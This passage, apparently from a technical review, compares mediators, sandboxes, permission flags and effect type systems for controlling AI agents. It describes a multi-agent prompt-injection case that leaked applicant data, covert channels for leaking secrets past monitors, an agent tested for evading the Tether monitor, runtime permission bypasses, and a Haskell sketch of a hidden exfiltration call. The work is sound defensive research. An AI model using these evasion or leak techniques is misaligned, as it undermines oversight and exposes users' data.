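Other work has extended the approach. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) reports that TACIT, which protects "classified" values with a type system and needs only one agent loop, has completion rates comparable to CaMeL's. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a screen and kept up to 57 percent of the performance of leading models. Policies are hard to write for such agents because a click can close a notice or delete a file, depending on what is under the pointer. An attacker who puts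 up a fake cookie notice cannot add steps to the plan, but can get the agent to follow a branch that the plan already contains.

### When the recipient acts

A mediator controls what a program sends, but not what the recipient does next. Some companies let their hosted language models search the web or run code while composing a reply. In McCann's formal model, a call to a language model is a single request whose reply can be anything. Mashin would record one model call, even if the model fetched ten web pages. Untrusted code in Mashin may call only language models, but a model with its own web tools would give that code indirect access to the web.

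Requests to ordinary services can also cause further effects. A payment company can announce each refund through a *webhook*, an automatic message to another company's web address. A database can run a stored procedure whenever a program changes a record, and that procedure might send an email. The ledger would contain the change but not the email. Whoever grants a permission therefore has to consider everything the recipient of a request can do in response. A company can reduce the risk by turning off a model's web tools or by using a database account that cannot start such procedures.

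Labels can disappear when one agent calls another. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three agents, each protected by CaMeL. The user asked for a summary of job applicants to be emailed to a colleague. One agent read the applicants' records from a database where the researchers had planted an instruction. The coordinating agent treated the records as untrusted data, but inserted a summary of them into its message to the agent that sends notifications. That agent treated the whole message as instructions from its user, so it also emailed the applicants' details to an outside address.

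A policy on recipients might not have stopped the email, because the notification agent had no reason to distrust the address. Peters-Gill and colleagues solved the problem by sending instructions and untrusted data separately and keeping the labels on the data. On their multi-agent version of AgentDojo, 12.9 percent of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2 percent with CaMeL on each agent, and none with the new method. The weakness was rare in these tests, but the researchers argue that almost any system of this kind has it. Agents completed fewer tasks with the new method, though the reduction was modest with the strongest models.

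Mashin can govern a called program if both programs run under the same mediator. McCann does not prove that governance still holds when a request crosses into another organisation.

### Signals without a message

In 1973 the computer scientist Butler Lampson described the *confinement problem*, which is how to make sure that another person's program does not pass on the private data it is given to work with. Even if files and messages are blocked, the program could hide information in the bill for its services, or in how heavily it loads the computer. Lampson called the second kind of leak a *covert channel*, because nobody intended it for communication.

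Governed programs have covert channels too. Tallam and Miller point out that a CaMeL program can repeat a harmless request a secret number of times, which reveals the number to the recipient. Differences in running time and errors that occur only for certain secrets can also leak information.

McCann leaves timing and power use outside his model in *Intent-Driven Computing*, but in *Certified Purity for Cognitive Workflow Executors* he claims that a certified executor cannot leak data through side channels because it has no means of input or output. This claim is too strong because the executor can send a timing signal by calculating for a longer or shorter time, though it would struggle to receive one because it cannot read a clock. A Mashin `compute` step can read the clock, so it could receive the signal.

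A program can also leak data through its pattern of refused requests. The mediator stops a forbidden request, but anyone who can read the ledger can see that the program made it. At one bit per request, a card number would take 54 requests. McCann's simulated refund agent had 312 refusals in 200 cases, so an auditor might not notice a few dozen more.

Tallam and Miller suggest limiting loops that depend on secrets, combining repeated requests, and making every sensitive operation take as long as its slowest case. These measures slow programs down, and most only reduce the leak. They matter most when a company gives secrets to a program it does not trust, since an encryption key is short enough to leak through even a very slow channel.

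### Allowed actions that add up to harm

McCann acknowledges that a program can also carry out a harmful plan if the policy allows each action in it. For example, the refund agent needs one customer's record for each case. If it reads 200 records a day and keeps a copy of each, it will have up to 73,000 after a year, although the policy permitted every lookup.

Rules about past actions, such as Sapien's, can limit totals and forbid certain sequences. By contrast, CaMeL's policies apply to individual moments and have no general way to express rules about a whole run, such as "every customer eventually gets an answer", according to *CaMeLoT* (2026). Even a policy with a complete history can miss a plan that several agents share, unless the mediator combines their records.

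The mediator also enforces a policy even if it is wrong. Labels add more rules that could be wrong, because someone must decide what counts as secret and where it may go. CaMeL needs a policy for each tool, so Tallam and Miller expect duplicated and inconsistent rules in organisations with hundreds of tools.

Asking a person to approve doubtful requests leaves that person to judge which ones are safe. Willison reports that the CaMeL paper lists user fatigue among the system's limitations, and warns that people who receive constant requests may start approving them without thinking. McCann's simulated refund agent needed more than one approval for every two customers.

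## How does it compare with guard libraries, permission flags and network controls?

A company that wants to limit its refund agent may not need a new language. It can add checks to the agent's Python code, choose a runtime with permissions, insert checks into the compiled program, or confine the running process from outside. A check closer to the network is harder for the code to bypass, but it usually has less information about what an action means.

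### A guard that every package has to choose

In Python, the company could send its refunds through a function of its own:

```python
import http.client, json

def refund(order, amount):
    if amount > 500:
        raise PermissionError("refund above $500")
    ledger.append((order, amount))
    body = json.dumps({"order": order, "amount": amount})
    conn = http.client.HTTPSConnection("payments.example.com")
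    conn.request("POST", "/refunds", body, {"Authorization": KEY})
    return conn.getresponse().read()
```

Here `KEY` is the company's access key for the payment service, and `ledger` is a list defined elsewhere in the module. A call for $900 raises an error, while a call for $120 adds an entry and sends the payment.

The date-formatting package can pay out $900 without calling `refund` or leaving an entry. The last four lines of that function use only the standard library, so the package can copy them and read `KEY` from the guard's module. To be sure that no refund bypasses the guard, someone has to read every package the program imports, directly or indirectly, and read them again after each update.

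The company could replace `http.client` with a checked version when the program starts, but a package could then use `socket`. A checked `socket` would not affect a C library that makes its own system calls.

Running the guard in a separate process that holds the only copy of the key works better. Other code can still contact the payment company, but the company will reject its requests. Every refund has to go through the guard, although a package could still send customer data somewhere else. In *From Intent to Execution Grant*, Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) specify a check that gives each approved action a single-use grant tied to its exact contents, such as a recipient and an amount. In each of 100 tests, exactly one of 32 simultaneous attempts to use the same grant succeeded. The researchers acknowledge that the check does not guarantee complete coverage. Whoever deploys it has to make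 the action require a grant and block other routes to it.

### Permission flags in Deno and Node.js

A runtime can put checks inside the built-in functions that every package needs for external effects. Deno, which runs JavaScript and TypeScript, works this way. According to Deno's *Security and permissions*, a program starts with no access to files, the network, environment variables or other programs, and the user grants access on the command line:

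```
deno run --allow-net=payments.example.com refunds.ts
```

The date-formatting package can now contact only the payment company. If it can get the key, it can still send a $900 refund, because the flag does not limit what a request contains. All code on the same thread has the same permissions. To give a package fewer permissions, a developer has to run it in a web worker, a separate thread that can have its own permissions.

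Deno lets programs use `eval` freely, since the evaluated code gets no extra permissions. It also loads every module that the source names in a fixed import, including modules from web addresses, without checking permissions. As in Dhall, a program can therefore cause network requests before it runs.

Two flags undo the protection. With `--allow-run`, a program can start other programs, and Deno's restrictions do not apply to them. A script that may run `deno` can start another copy of Deno with every permission. Allowing only specific programs is still risky if the script can write to the folders that contain them, because it can replace them. With `--allow-ffi`, a script can load native libraries, which make system calls directly. Deno advises users to treat both flags as equivalent to allowing everything, and to run untrusted code inside an operating system sandbox or a virtual machine.

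Deno can also send every permission check to a separate process called a *broker*, which replaces the flags. The broker returns "allow" or "deny", and Deno stops the program if the connection to the broker fails. A company could use a broker to apply a central policy and log each decision, which would make it much like a mediator. However, the broker receives only the process number, the time, the kind of permission and a value such as a file path, not the name of the package that made the request or the size of a refund.

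Node.js, the older runtime for JavaScript programs, gives code full access unless the user adds the `--permission` flag. The flag's restrictions did not cover the network in version 24, but they do in version 26. Node.js' *Permissions* compares the feature to a seat belt that keeps trusted code from using resources by accident, and warns that malicious code can bypass it. For example, a program can use files that are already open, or follow a symbolic link out of a permitted folder. Even a program with no permissions can make another Node.js process under the same user account open its debugging interface.

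Node.js has an audit mode that reports operations the program lacks permission for and lets them proceed. This helps a developer write a policy, but the mode does not report permitted operations, so its reports are not a complete record of the program's external effects.

### Why Java gave up its Security Manager

Java had a more detailed permission system for about 25 years. OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021), a proposal from the project that develops Java, traces the system to Java 1.0, when web browsers downloaded and ran small programs called applets. Java's library had only eight packages, so its developers could make each sensitive function call a component called the Security Manager, which allowed operations for code on the user's machine and blocked them for applets.

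Java 1.2 treated all code as untrusted by default and let users give each body of code its own permissions. A user could have denied network access to the date-formatting package while allowing it for the refund code. Deno cannot give different permissions to code running in the same thread.

This precision made the system hard to use. Before an operation, the Security Manager checked the permissions of all the code that had led to it. If the refund code called a logging library that wrote to a file, the refund code needed permission to write to that file too. A library could limit this check to its own permissions, but the rules for doing so safely were complicated. Developers also had to list every permission their program needed, even if they only wanted to restrict which files it could read. OpenJDK adds that the checks were often too slow and could not address 19 of the 25 most dangerous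 kinds of software weakness on a 2020 industry list.

Java's maintainers had to support the Security Manager even though few people used it. *JEP 486* (Mullan and Buckley, 2024) counts over 1,000 library methods that had to check permissions and over 1,200 that had to use their own permissions even if the calling program lacked them. For example, Java reads a time-zone file when a program asks for the local time, so the time library needed to read that file even if the program wasn't allowed to. Most applications that enabled the Security Manager granted all permissions to their code.

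OpenJDK deprecated the Security Manager in Java 17 and disabled it in JDK 24. Mullan and Buckley recommend restricting Java programs from outside, with containers, virtual machines or operating system features such as seccomp.

McCann's design has an advantage over Java's. Java's developers had to put checks in more than 1,000 places and could overlook one, whereas all 14 kinds of request in Mashin's formal model go through the same mediator. But Mashin's users still have to work out which permissions each program needs. If they find this too tedious, they may grant every permission, as Java's users did.

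Some projects had relied on the Security Manager to restrict plugins. The developers of OpenSearch, a search engine that runs plugins in its own process, found no single replacement. Version 3.0 combines operating system restrictions on the whole process with a component that modifies Java classes as they load. The added code checks which plugin is opening a file or network connection, but it does not cover everything the Security Manager did. Elasticsearch, another search engine, has a similar system that denies plugins network access unless they declare it. Elastic's *Entitlements* warns that native code may get around the checks. Developers of Apache Solr, also a search engine, have proposed adapting OpenSearch's component because Solr otherwise has no such protection on Java 24 or later.

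### Monitors woven into the program

OpenSearch's component is an *inlined monitor*, a set of checks that a tool inserts into compiled code. Princeton researchers had developed Polymer, a language for writing such monitors, more than 20 years earlier, and first described it in *A Calculus for Composing Security Policies* (Bauer, Ligatti and Walker, 2002). One of their example policies lets a program use files or the network, but not both, so it cannot read a private file and send it over the network.

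*Composing Security Policies with Polymer* (Bauer, Ligatti and Walker, 2005) describes a system in which a programmer lists the methods that could affect security. Before Java starts, a tool modifies its libraries so that calls to those methods go to a security policy first. The system makes the same changes to the application's code while that code loads. The policy can let a call proceed, run other code first, substitute its own result, raise an error or stop the program.

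In Polymer's notation, a limit on refunds would look roughly like this:

```java
public Sug query(Action a) {
  aswitch(a) {
    case <abs void Refund(String order, int amount)>:
      if (amount > 500) return new ExnSug(this, a);
      return new OKSug(this, a);
  }
  return new IrrSug(this);
}
```

`ExnSug` raises an error, `OKSug` permits the call, and `IrrSug` permits calls that the policy does not cover. `Refund` is an *abstract action*, a name for all the methods that can send a refund. This lets the policy's author write the rule in business terms, as with a well-designed effect request. However, the author has to identify those methods correctly.

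Bauer and colleagues tested Polymer on Pooka, an email program with about 50,000 lines of code, which they did not have to inspect or change. Their policy, which was about 1,800 lines long, logged messages, prompted the user to confirm recipients and restricted network connections. It also blocked operating system commands and malicious uses of reflection and class loading, which could otherwise let a program bypass the checks. Modifying all 28,742 methods in Java's standard packages took 107 seconds. Each call to the policy added about 0.62 milliseconds on a computer of that time, slightly more than Mashin's 0.535 milliseconds, which includes writing to the ledger.

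Polymer could thus give an existing Java program many of a mediator's abilities, including readable rules, memory of earlier actions and a log. However, it applies the policy only to calls to methods on its list. If a new version of a library adds another method for opening a connection and nobody updates the list, calls to that method go unchecked. Native code can also make system calls without calling any listed method.

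### Control from outside the process

Operating system controls do not need a list of library methods, because ordinary code in any language must go through the kernel to open a file or connection. *Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) describes how Nvidia's OpenShell runtime uses these controls to confine AI agents. The agent runs in a sandbox with a small helper process, which uses the Linux feature seccomp to intercept every socket call and forwards it to a supervisor outside. The supervisor checks the policy, opens the real connection, adds any access keys and passes the data along. Another Linux feature, Landlock, limits which files the agent can reach, and an outer barrier blocks every network route except the one to the supervisor.

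If the refund agent ran in this sandbox, connections from the refund code, the date-formatting package and C libraries would all go through the same check. The package could not steal `KEY`, because the supervisor would hold `KEY` outside the Python program.

An agent that took over the supervisor could still change the policy. Airlock, by Abdollahi and colleagues, therefore runs the agent and the supervisor in separate virtual machines, and the processor protects each machine's memory from the other machine and from the host. Even an agent that controlled its own operating system could not alter the policy or the log. In tests, Airlock reduced file system performance by less than 15 percent and network bandwidth by at least half.

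### How Tether follows data between commands

A sandbox that checks each connection separately can miss a leak that takes several steps. Tether, the Google DeepMind system that enforces policy on observed side effects, also tracks where data has been. Sistla and colleagues give the example of an agent that is allowed to read a sensitive file, `servers.csv`, and to upload public status reports to GitHub.

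| Command | What Tether infers | Label on `report.txt` afterwards | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Upload `report.txt` | A file goes to GitHub | Public | Allow |
| Copy `servers.csv` over `report.txt` | Sensitive data moves to the report | Sensitive | Allow |
| Upload `report.txt` again | A sensitive file would go to GitHub | Sensitive | Refuse |

The first and third commands are identical, so a fixed list of permitted commands could not separate them.

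Tether runs each command in a temporary layer over the file system, so changes affect only a disposable copy. It traces the command's system calls and holds outgoing network requests at a proxy. It then translates these calls and requests into 11 kinds of action, such as reading, copying and uploading, and checks them against the policy. If the policy allows them all, Tether makes the file changes permanent. Otherwise it discards them.

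Network requests are harder to reverse. The proxy forwards a request if everything the command has done so far complies with the policy. A script could therefore send a permitted refund, mark the order as refunded in a local file, and then attempt something forbidden. Tether would discard the change to the file, but the refund would already have been sent, so the next run might send it again.

Tether cannot determine exactly how a program uses the data it reads, so if a process reads `a.txt` and then writes `b.txt`, Tether treats `b.txt` as possibly containing data from `a.txt`.

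Sistla and colleagues wrote the policy in the proof assistant Lean and proved seven properties of it for action sequences of any length, including that data labeled "secret" never leaves the local network. The proofs assume that Tether infers actions correctly. The researchers could only test that assumption, much as McCann tested Mashin's runtime against his model. They generated random file operations and had an AI agent try to get past the monitor. The agent's success rate fell from 40 percent to zero over three versions as they fixed gaps such as a failure to track hard links, which are second names for the same file.

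They then replayed recorded runs of coding agents from two benchmarks and compared Tether with Auto Mode, a feature of Anthropic's Claude Code in which a language model reviews each command.

| Monitor | Attacks blocked, of 344 | Harmless runs blocked, of 1,590 |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 (100%) | 74 (4.7%) |
| Auto Mode | 315 (91.6%) | 155 (9.7%) |
| Auto Mode with Tether's policy as instructions | 307 (89.2%) | 55 (3.5%) |

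Of Tether's 74 false alarms, 50 involved unrequested changes to protected files, and seven involved undeclared websites. The other 17 came from reads of sensitive files. For example, searching every file for a word also opens the secret ones, and Tether then treats the agent as having read them.

These results cover only runs whose actions Tether can model. The researchers estimate that 28.2 percent of runs in one benchmark and 22.1 percent in the other would need a monitor that understands content, for example one that can recognise malicious code in a file the agent was supposed to edit. Tether cannot yet follow data through databases or background processes, though a stricter policy can block both. The researchers refined the policy by testing drafts on benchmark runs, so it may raise more false alarms on unfamiliar tasks.

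Tether would be a useful addition to Mashin because the runtime could run `exec` scripts inside it and check their file and network operations without anyone rewriting the scripts.

### When is outside enforcement enough?

From outside, a company can control which programs a process starts, which files it opens and which addresses it contacts. Most web traffic is encrypted, so an ordinary proxy cannot read details such as the amount of a refund. A proxy that decrypts traffic can, but the program has to accept the proxy's certificate. So far, Tether decrypts only traffic to simulated services. If a program encrypts data itself before sending it, neither a decrypting proxy nor Mashin's mediator can read the data.

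For the refund agent, a sandbox whose only exit is a decrypting proxy could enforce most of the company's policy. The proxy could hold the payment key, refuse amounts above $500 and log every request. If order lookups also went through it, it could reject a refund for an order that the agent had not looked up. The agent could stay in Python and keep using its packages and native libraries. For network requests, this sandbox would give an existing program the complete governance that McCann says no library can add.

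The purpose of an action is harder to establish from outside the program. Abdollahi and colleagues acknowledge that Airlock's guarantees do not cover the intent behind a permitted action. A proxy can read an order number and an amount, but it cannot tell which step of the program produced them or whether the amount came from the company's records or a customer's email. A language runtime can have that information, though Mashin does not yet track where values come from. No mediator can determine whether the agent had a good reason for a refund.

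Approvals are also awkward with a proxy. It can hold a $350 refund until a manager responds, but the connection will probably time out, and the agent needs extra code to try again later. Mashin can save the program's state and resume it three days later.

A new language is therefore unnecessary if the company's rules concern files, destinations and the readable contents of requests. It is more useful if the rules depend on information inside the program, or if programs often wait for people. Even then, the company should keep the outside sandbox as a second barrier.

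| Approach | What it covers | What it can miss | What it records | What one has to trust |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Guard library | Calls through the library, with their arguments | Packages that use another route | Whatever the library logs | Every package in the program |
| Deno permissions | Files, network hosts, environment variables and program starts | Request contents, and anything a subprocess or native library does | Permission checks, if a broker logs them | Deno, plus any programs and native libraries it may use |
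| Node.js permissions | Accidental use of files, the network and other programs | Malicious code | In audit mode, operations without permission | All the code in the program |
| Java's Security Manager, before JDK 24 | Over 1,000 library methods, with separate permissions for each body of code | Harmful data that permitted code processes | Whatever a custom version logged | Java's virtual machine and libraries |
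| Inlined monitor, such as Polymer | Calls to listed methods, with their arguments | Unlisted methods and native code | Whatever the policy logs | The list, the rewriting tool and Java |
| Sandbox with a proxy | Files, processes and connections, in any language | The purpose of an action, and contents the proxy cannot decrypt | Connections, and request contents if the proxy decrypts them | The kernel, the sandbox and the proxy |
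| Tether | The same effects, plus data that moves between files | Harmful content in permitted files, and most encrypted traffic | System calls and network requests for each command | The kernel, the tracer, the proxy, the code that infers actions, and Lean |
| Mashin | Every effect request, with its arguments and context | What `exec` scripts and outside services do next | Requests and decisions, unless the program disables the record | The mediator, the rest of the runtime and the host |

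## How does it compare with types and capabilities that track effects?

Mashin's mediator and an outside sandbox both stop a forbidden action when a program attempts it, whereas a type checker can reject the program before it starts. In a language with an effect system, a function's type lists its inputs, its result and the effects it may have, and the compiler rejects code that could have any other effect. Several research groups applied this idea to AI agents in 2026. Their results bear on McCann's argument that analysing programs can never govern all of the programs' effects.

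### Effects in a function's type

In Haskell, two functions from the refund program could have these types:

```haskell
refundAmount :: Int -> Int -> Int
sendRefund   :: String -> Int -> IO String
```

`refundAmount` takes a price and a fee and returns a number. `sendRefund` takes an order number and an amount and returns an `IO` action, which produces a refund number when performed. If `refundAmount` called `sendRefund`, it could not perform the resulting action, because `refundAmount` must return a plain number. Any function that uses the payment company's reply therefore has `IO` in its type too. If a date-formatting function has the type `Day -> String`, a reader can conclude that it sends nothing, with one exception described below.

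`IO` is a coarse label, since printing a line and wiping a disk both have it. Koka, a research language by Daan Leijen, lists the kinds of effect separately:

```koka
fun refund-amount( price : int, fee : int ) : total int
fun send-refund( order : string, amount : int ) : <net,exn> string
```

Here `total` means that the function has no effects and always finishes. `send-refund` may use the network and may raise an exception. If a function calls both, its type includes the effects of both, except for `exn` if it catches the exception. Koka's compiler can usually infer the effects, so programmers don't have to write them everywhere.

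McCann objects that effect systems keep no tamper-evident record and do not force every effect through one mediator. This is true of Haskell and Koka by default, but a company can use their types to impose both requirements.

### Replacing IO for a whole program

The company would define its own type and accept only programs that have it:

```haskell
data Governed a    -- the module exports no constructors

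ask     :: Request -> Governed Reply
program :: Governed ()
run     :: Policy -> Governed () -> IO ()
```

A value of type `Governed a` describes a computation that may request effects and then returns a value of type `a`. The programmer writes `program` and can use `ask`, pure code and the usual operators for joining steps. Only the runtime can call `run`, which executes the program, passes each request to the mediator and gives the program the reply or refusal.

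No function turns an `IO` action into a `Governed` one, so a governed program that calls an ordinary networking library does not compile. The date-formatting package may still contain a function that opens a connection, but a governed program cannot perform the resulting action. Haskell thus uses a type to enforce the restriction that Mashin enforces through its grammar, and the compiler checks it before the program runs.

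McCann's proofs rely on a type in the same way. In *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance*, a program has the type `itree DirectiveE R`, a tree whose only events are requests. McCann writes that "the type system does the work" in his theorem about programs that run other programs. In *The Two Boundaries*, he draws two distinctions between his design and Haskell. The first is that Haskell enforces purity at compile time, while his design removes the power to act at run time, which is a difference in implementation. The second, that `IO` actions execute without any check or record, no longer applies once `run` checks and records them.

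The Haskell version's guarantee holds only at the source level. The compiler produces ordinary machine code that could make any system call, so the company has to trust the compiler, the libraries and the module that defines `Governed`.

### The exception and how Safe Haskell excludes it

Haskell has an escape hatch with a short type:

```haskell
unsafePerformIO :: IO a -> a
```

It turns an action into a plain value by performing the action whenever something needs the value. The date-formatting package could use it like this:

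```haskell
formatDate :: Day -> String
formatDate day = unsafePerformIO (do
  sendToStranger (show day)
  return (show day))
```

The type still marks the code as pure, but using the formatted date sends a message. Library authors have legitimate reasons to use the function, such as wrapping a C routine that behaves like a mathematical function.

Safe Haskell is a restricted form of Haskell that programmers turn on with a compiler setting. According to *Language-Based Agent Control*, it leaves out `unsafePerformIO` and similar features. A module in safe mode may import only modules that the compiler has checked in the same way or that their authors have marked as trustworthy, and the module that exports `unsafePerformIO` is neither. Safe mode also requires every function imported from C to have an `IO` type, so a program cannot treat a C function as pure.

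The compiler does not check whether modules labelled trustworthy deserve the label. They may use unsafe features internally, and their authors vouch for the result. Someone at the company would have to decide which of these modules to accept, much as Joe-E's designers had to judge Java's library methods.

### Agents that write Haskell

*Language-Based Agent Control* presents ELBA, a Haskell library for programs that include AI agents. A developer calls the function `agent` with a prompt, a list of definitions the agent may use and the expected result type. ELBA asks a language model for a program, checks its type and runs it only if it passes. If the check fails, ELBA returns the compiler's error to the model and asks for another attempt.

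If the developer expects an `Int`, the agent can only calculate. If a user asked it to delete the server's files and then work out a factorial, a program that did both would have the type `IO Int`, and ELBA would reject it.

An agent that needs external effects gets a custom effect type. The bibliography agent must write a program of type `BibIO ()`, which can search DBLP (a database of computer science papers), fetch an entry or add one to a file. The function that writes to the file accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`, and only the fetching function can create them. The agent can sort and filter entries but cannot make one up. In 100 tasks, ELBA wrote 925 citations, none with a wrong author, year or identifier. An ordinary agent with a web search tool got 19 of 1,002 wrong.

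A generated program can call `agent` again, and the new program must fit the type of the surrounding code. A parent agent can therefore give a child fewer powers than its own, but not more. McCann's rules for generated programs let a new program keep a permission but drop a condition attached to it. In ELBA, the child inherits conditions such as "only entries from DBLP" because they are built into the operations that the type allows.

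The researchers prove that if Haskell's types guarantee a property for all ordinary programs, the property also holds for programs that call agents. They replace each call with an ordinary function that queries the model, checks the reply and runs it. The result is an ordinary well-typed program, so the guarantee is only as strong as Haskell's own.

For secrets and untrusted data, ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library that labels data and checks the labels while the program runs. The researchers tested this on AgentDojo's Slack tasks. All four models resisted all 105 attacks even without the labels, so they simulated a worse case in which any sub-agent that read an attacker's instructions carried them out. Each model faced 735 of these simulated attacks.

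| Model | Attacks resisted with policies | Attacks resisted without | Tasks completed with policies | Tasks completed without |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 | 351 | 523 |
| Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 | 312 | 557 |
| GPT 5.4 | 735 | 621 | 338 | 558 |
| Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 | 294 | 494 |

The policies stopped every attack, but they reduced the share of tasks completed by 23 to 33 percentage points. Type checking caused hardly any of this loss. Models failed to produce a well-typed program within the permitted attempts in only 7 of 2,688 runs, and retries took 3.4 percent of the running time. The tasks failed mostly because the label rules forbid some legitimate actions. Without attacks, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of the 21 Slack tasks with its policies on, compared with 4 to 6 for CaMeL, but ELBA took about three times as long.

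### Secrets that code can use but not reveal

In a language such as Joe-E, a programmer controls which code receives a capability, but a function's type does not show which capabilities the function has kept. Scala 3's experimental *capture checking* adds this information to the type. The type `String ->{f} Unit` describes a function that takes text, returns nothing and may use the capability `f`, while `String -> Unit` describes a function that holds no capabilities.

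*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* uses this distinction in TACIT, a tool from the Swiss university EPFL that compiles and runs Scala code written by AI agents. When an agent reads a file from a protected folder, TACIT wraps the text in a container called `Classified`. The agent can apply a function to the contents with `map`, which accepts only pure functions. If `f` is a file the agent may write to, the compiler treats two attempts differently:

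```scala
val secret: Classified[String] = readClassified("key.txt")

secret.map(s => s.length)      // accepted
secret.map(s => f.write(s))    // rejected, because the function uses f
```

The accepted line produces another `Classified` value, so the length is protected too. If the agent prints it, the agent's own model receives only `Classified(****)`, while the user sees the number on a separate channel. To summarise a secret document, the agent can pass it to a second, trusted model, whose reply is also classified. The agent may write to `f`, but the compiler rejects the write if the text comes from a secret, a distinction that a permission to write files could not make.

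Capture checking can also limit how long a capability lasts. An agent asks for access to a folder by supplying a block of code, and the access ends when the block does. If the block returns a function that keeps the capability, the function's type lists that capability, and the compiler rejects the program. A Joe-E program, by contrast, can keep any reference it has received.

Agents have to write in Scala's *safe mode*, which forbids unchecked type conversions, reflection and other features that could stop the compiler from tracking a capability. As in Safe Haskell, library authors can exempt a module and take responsibility for it. Machine-checked proofs cover the core of capture checking, but nobody has yet proved that safe mode as a whole provides its intended guarantees.

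The researchers gave agents 12 tasks in a project with a folder of secrets and ran each task with each of 10 hidden attacks, for 120 trials. In 11 further trials, the user asked for the secrets directly or under a pretext. With `Classified`, no secret reached the agent's output in any of the 131 trials for either model. When the secrets were plain text, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked them in 2 trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11.

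On the standard AgentDojo tasks, one of 1,926 attacks succeeded. In that case, an agent quoted hotel reviews in which the attacker had recommended another hotel, and the policy allowed this because the reviews were public. With one of the two models, OpenAI's o4-mini-high, TACIT completed fewer tasks than CaMeL in all four categories. In the office category, TACIT completed 52.9 percent of tasks and CaMeL completed 81.4 percent.

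The models seemed to have little trouble writing Scala. On simulated customer service tasks, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher when they wrote Scala than when they called tools in the usual way. On coding tasks, the one model tested scored 1.7 points lower with Scala. Depending on the model and the task, 0.3 to 7.9 percent of the Scala snippets needed another attempt.

TACIT shares some of Mashin's gaps. A program that an agent starts from Scala is outside the type system, just as an `exec` script is outside Mashin's rules. A pure function can also reveal a little about a secret through how long it takes to run.

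Two later projects build on the same foundation. In *LACUNA* (2026), a language model fills gaps in a program, and optional capture checking lets the new code call a tool only if the needed capability is available at that point. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) extends Scala's types so that a programmer can include or exclude a whole kind of capability without naming each one. Its type safety proof is machine-checked in Lean.

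### Contracts on the order of requests

A list of effects does not show their order. A function that requests approval and then pays has the same list as one that pays first. Tan, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *ETAS*, describe a language for AI agents that checks order as well. In their notation, a refund function could look like this:

```
spec ApprovedRefund = Approval.request >> Payment.refund;

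flow refund(r: Refund) -> unit
  ![Approval.request, Payment.refund] ~ ApprovedRefund {
  if perform Approval.request(r) {
    perform Payment.refund(r);
  }
}
```

The list after the exclamation mark contains the effects the function may have. The tilde attaches a contract, in which `>>` means that an approval request must come before a refund. The compiler works out which sequences of requests the function could make and checks them with a small state machine built from the contract. If every sequence complies, as here, the compiler has proved that the function follows the contract. If every sequence breaks the contract, the compiler rejects the program. If only some sequences comply, the program may run, but a monitor checks each request and stops the first one that would break the contract.

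The compiler combines these sequences across function calls, including calls to other agents. Tan and colleagues cite a real case where an agent needed approval for certain tools, but another agent it had started used them without asking. In Koka, handling an effect removes it from the type, so a trial run that uses a test handler instead of contacting the payment company could skip the approval step unnoticed. ETAS would report the mistake because it keeps a request in the sequence even when a test handler answers it.

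The contract requires an approval request before the first refund but not before later ones, so an unapproved refund of $900 could follow an approved one of $120. McCann's well-governed traces have the same weakness. The contract also doesn't require the request to be granted. The `if` checks for that, but whoever writes the program could leave it out.

ETAS therefore has the host check the actual arguments and the history before it performs an action. A company could enforce its $500 limit in this check. The runtime also adds each request to an append-only trace and records whether a test handler answered it, the host performed it or a check refused it. ETAS is closer to Mashin than ELBA or TACIT is, because it has both a mediator and a record, although the ETAS trace has no hash chain. Tan and colleagues prove that the requests in every run obey the contract. Like McCann, they assume that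 the host mediates every external action.

The safety features have had only light testing. Ten scripted scenarios with part of a coding agent produced the expected results, as did six small compiler tests, four of which contained deliberate mistakes. Nobody tried to attack the system. Knowing which code is pure also lets a compiler rearrange that code safely. Such rearrangements reduced running time by 23.2 percent on 26 artificial workflows.

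### Does Rice's theorem rule this out?

McCann's main argument against analysing programs relies on Rice's theorem. It shows that no algorithm can correctly decide, for every program, whether the program's behaviour has a given property, if some programs have that property and others lack it. Having only effects that comply with the policy is such a property. McCann concludes that any approach that judges the behaviour of arbitrary programs must leave gaps, and that designers should judge effect requests instead.

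The theorem rules out only an algorithm that, in McCann's definition, allows a program if and only if the program complies. Such an algorithm must reject every harmful program and accept every harmless one. An algorithm that rejects every program meets the first requirement but is useless. Practical checkers reject every harmful program and accept many, but not all, harmless ones.

Type checkers reject some harmless programs. By Rice's theorem, no algorithm can decide for every program whether its result is a string. *A Programming Language Oriented Approach to Computability* (2014) explains that Java compilers therefore accept only programs for which they can prove such a property, and reject infinitely many reasonable ones. *Software is infrastructure* (2025) gives the example of a function that applies its argument to itself, which is harmless but fails the type systems in common use.

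McCann concedes most of the premises. In *Intent-Driven Computing*, he writes more carefully that no analysis can be "simultaneously sound, complete, and decidable", which leaves room for a sound, decidable analysis that is incomplete. He also accepts that approximate checkers may miss violations, raise false alarms or both, and that some restricted languages allow exact answers. A checker whose only errors are false alarms still lets no ungoverned effect through, so Rice's theorem gives no reason to prefer a mediator to a sound type system.

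McCann also applies the theorem to runtime monitors, saying they cannot determine in general whether a program's next action will break a policy. Monitors cannot always predict the action, but they do not need to if they intercept it, as McCann's own mediator does.

Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, gives an example that separates the approaches. A program searches the even numbers for one that is not the sum of two primes, and does something forbidden only if it finds one. It is harmless exactly if Goldbach's conjecture, an open problem in mathematics, is true. Suppose that the forbidden act is sending out the customer list:

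- A perfect checker would have to settle the conjecture.
- Koka's compiler would put `net` in the program's type and refuse to use the program where the network is off limits, whether or not the conjecture is true.
- Mashin would run the program and deny the request if the search ever succeeded.

Both Koka and Mashin would prevent the list from being sent out. However, Koka may reject a harmless program, while Mashin may allow a program that searches forever.

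Pérez-Acle proves that, for a simple ban, watching a program will eventually reveal any violation, but no set of checkable rules can clear every safe program. Any reliable set of rules *n* bits long fails to clear a safe program of about *n* bits. A checkable list can still include every program that must be accepted and none that must be refused, as long as not every safe program must be accepted. In simulations with 2.2 million random programs, the hard cases were rare and mostly constructed by an adversary.

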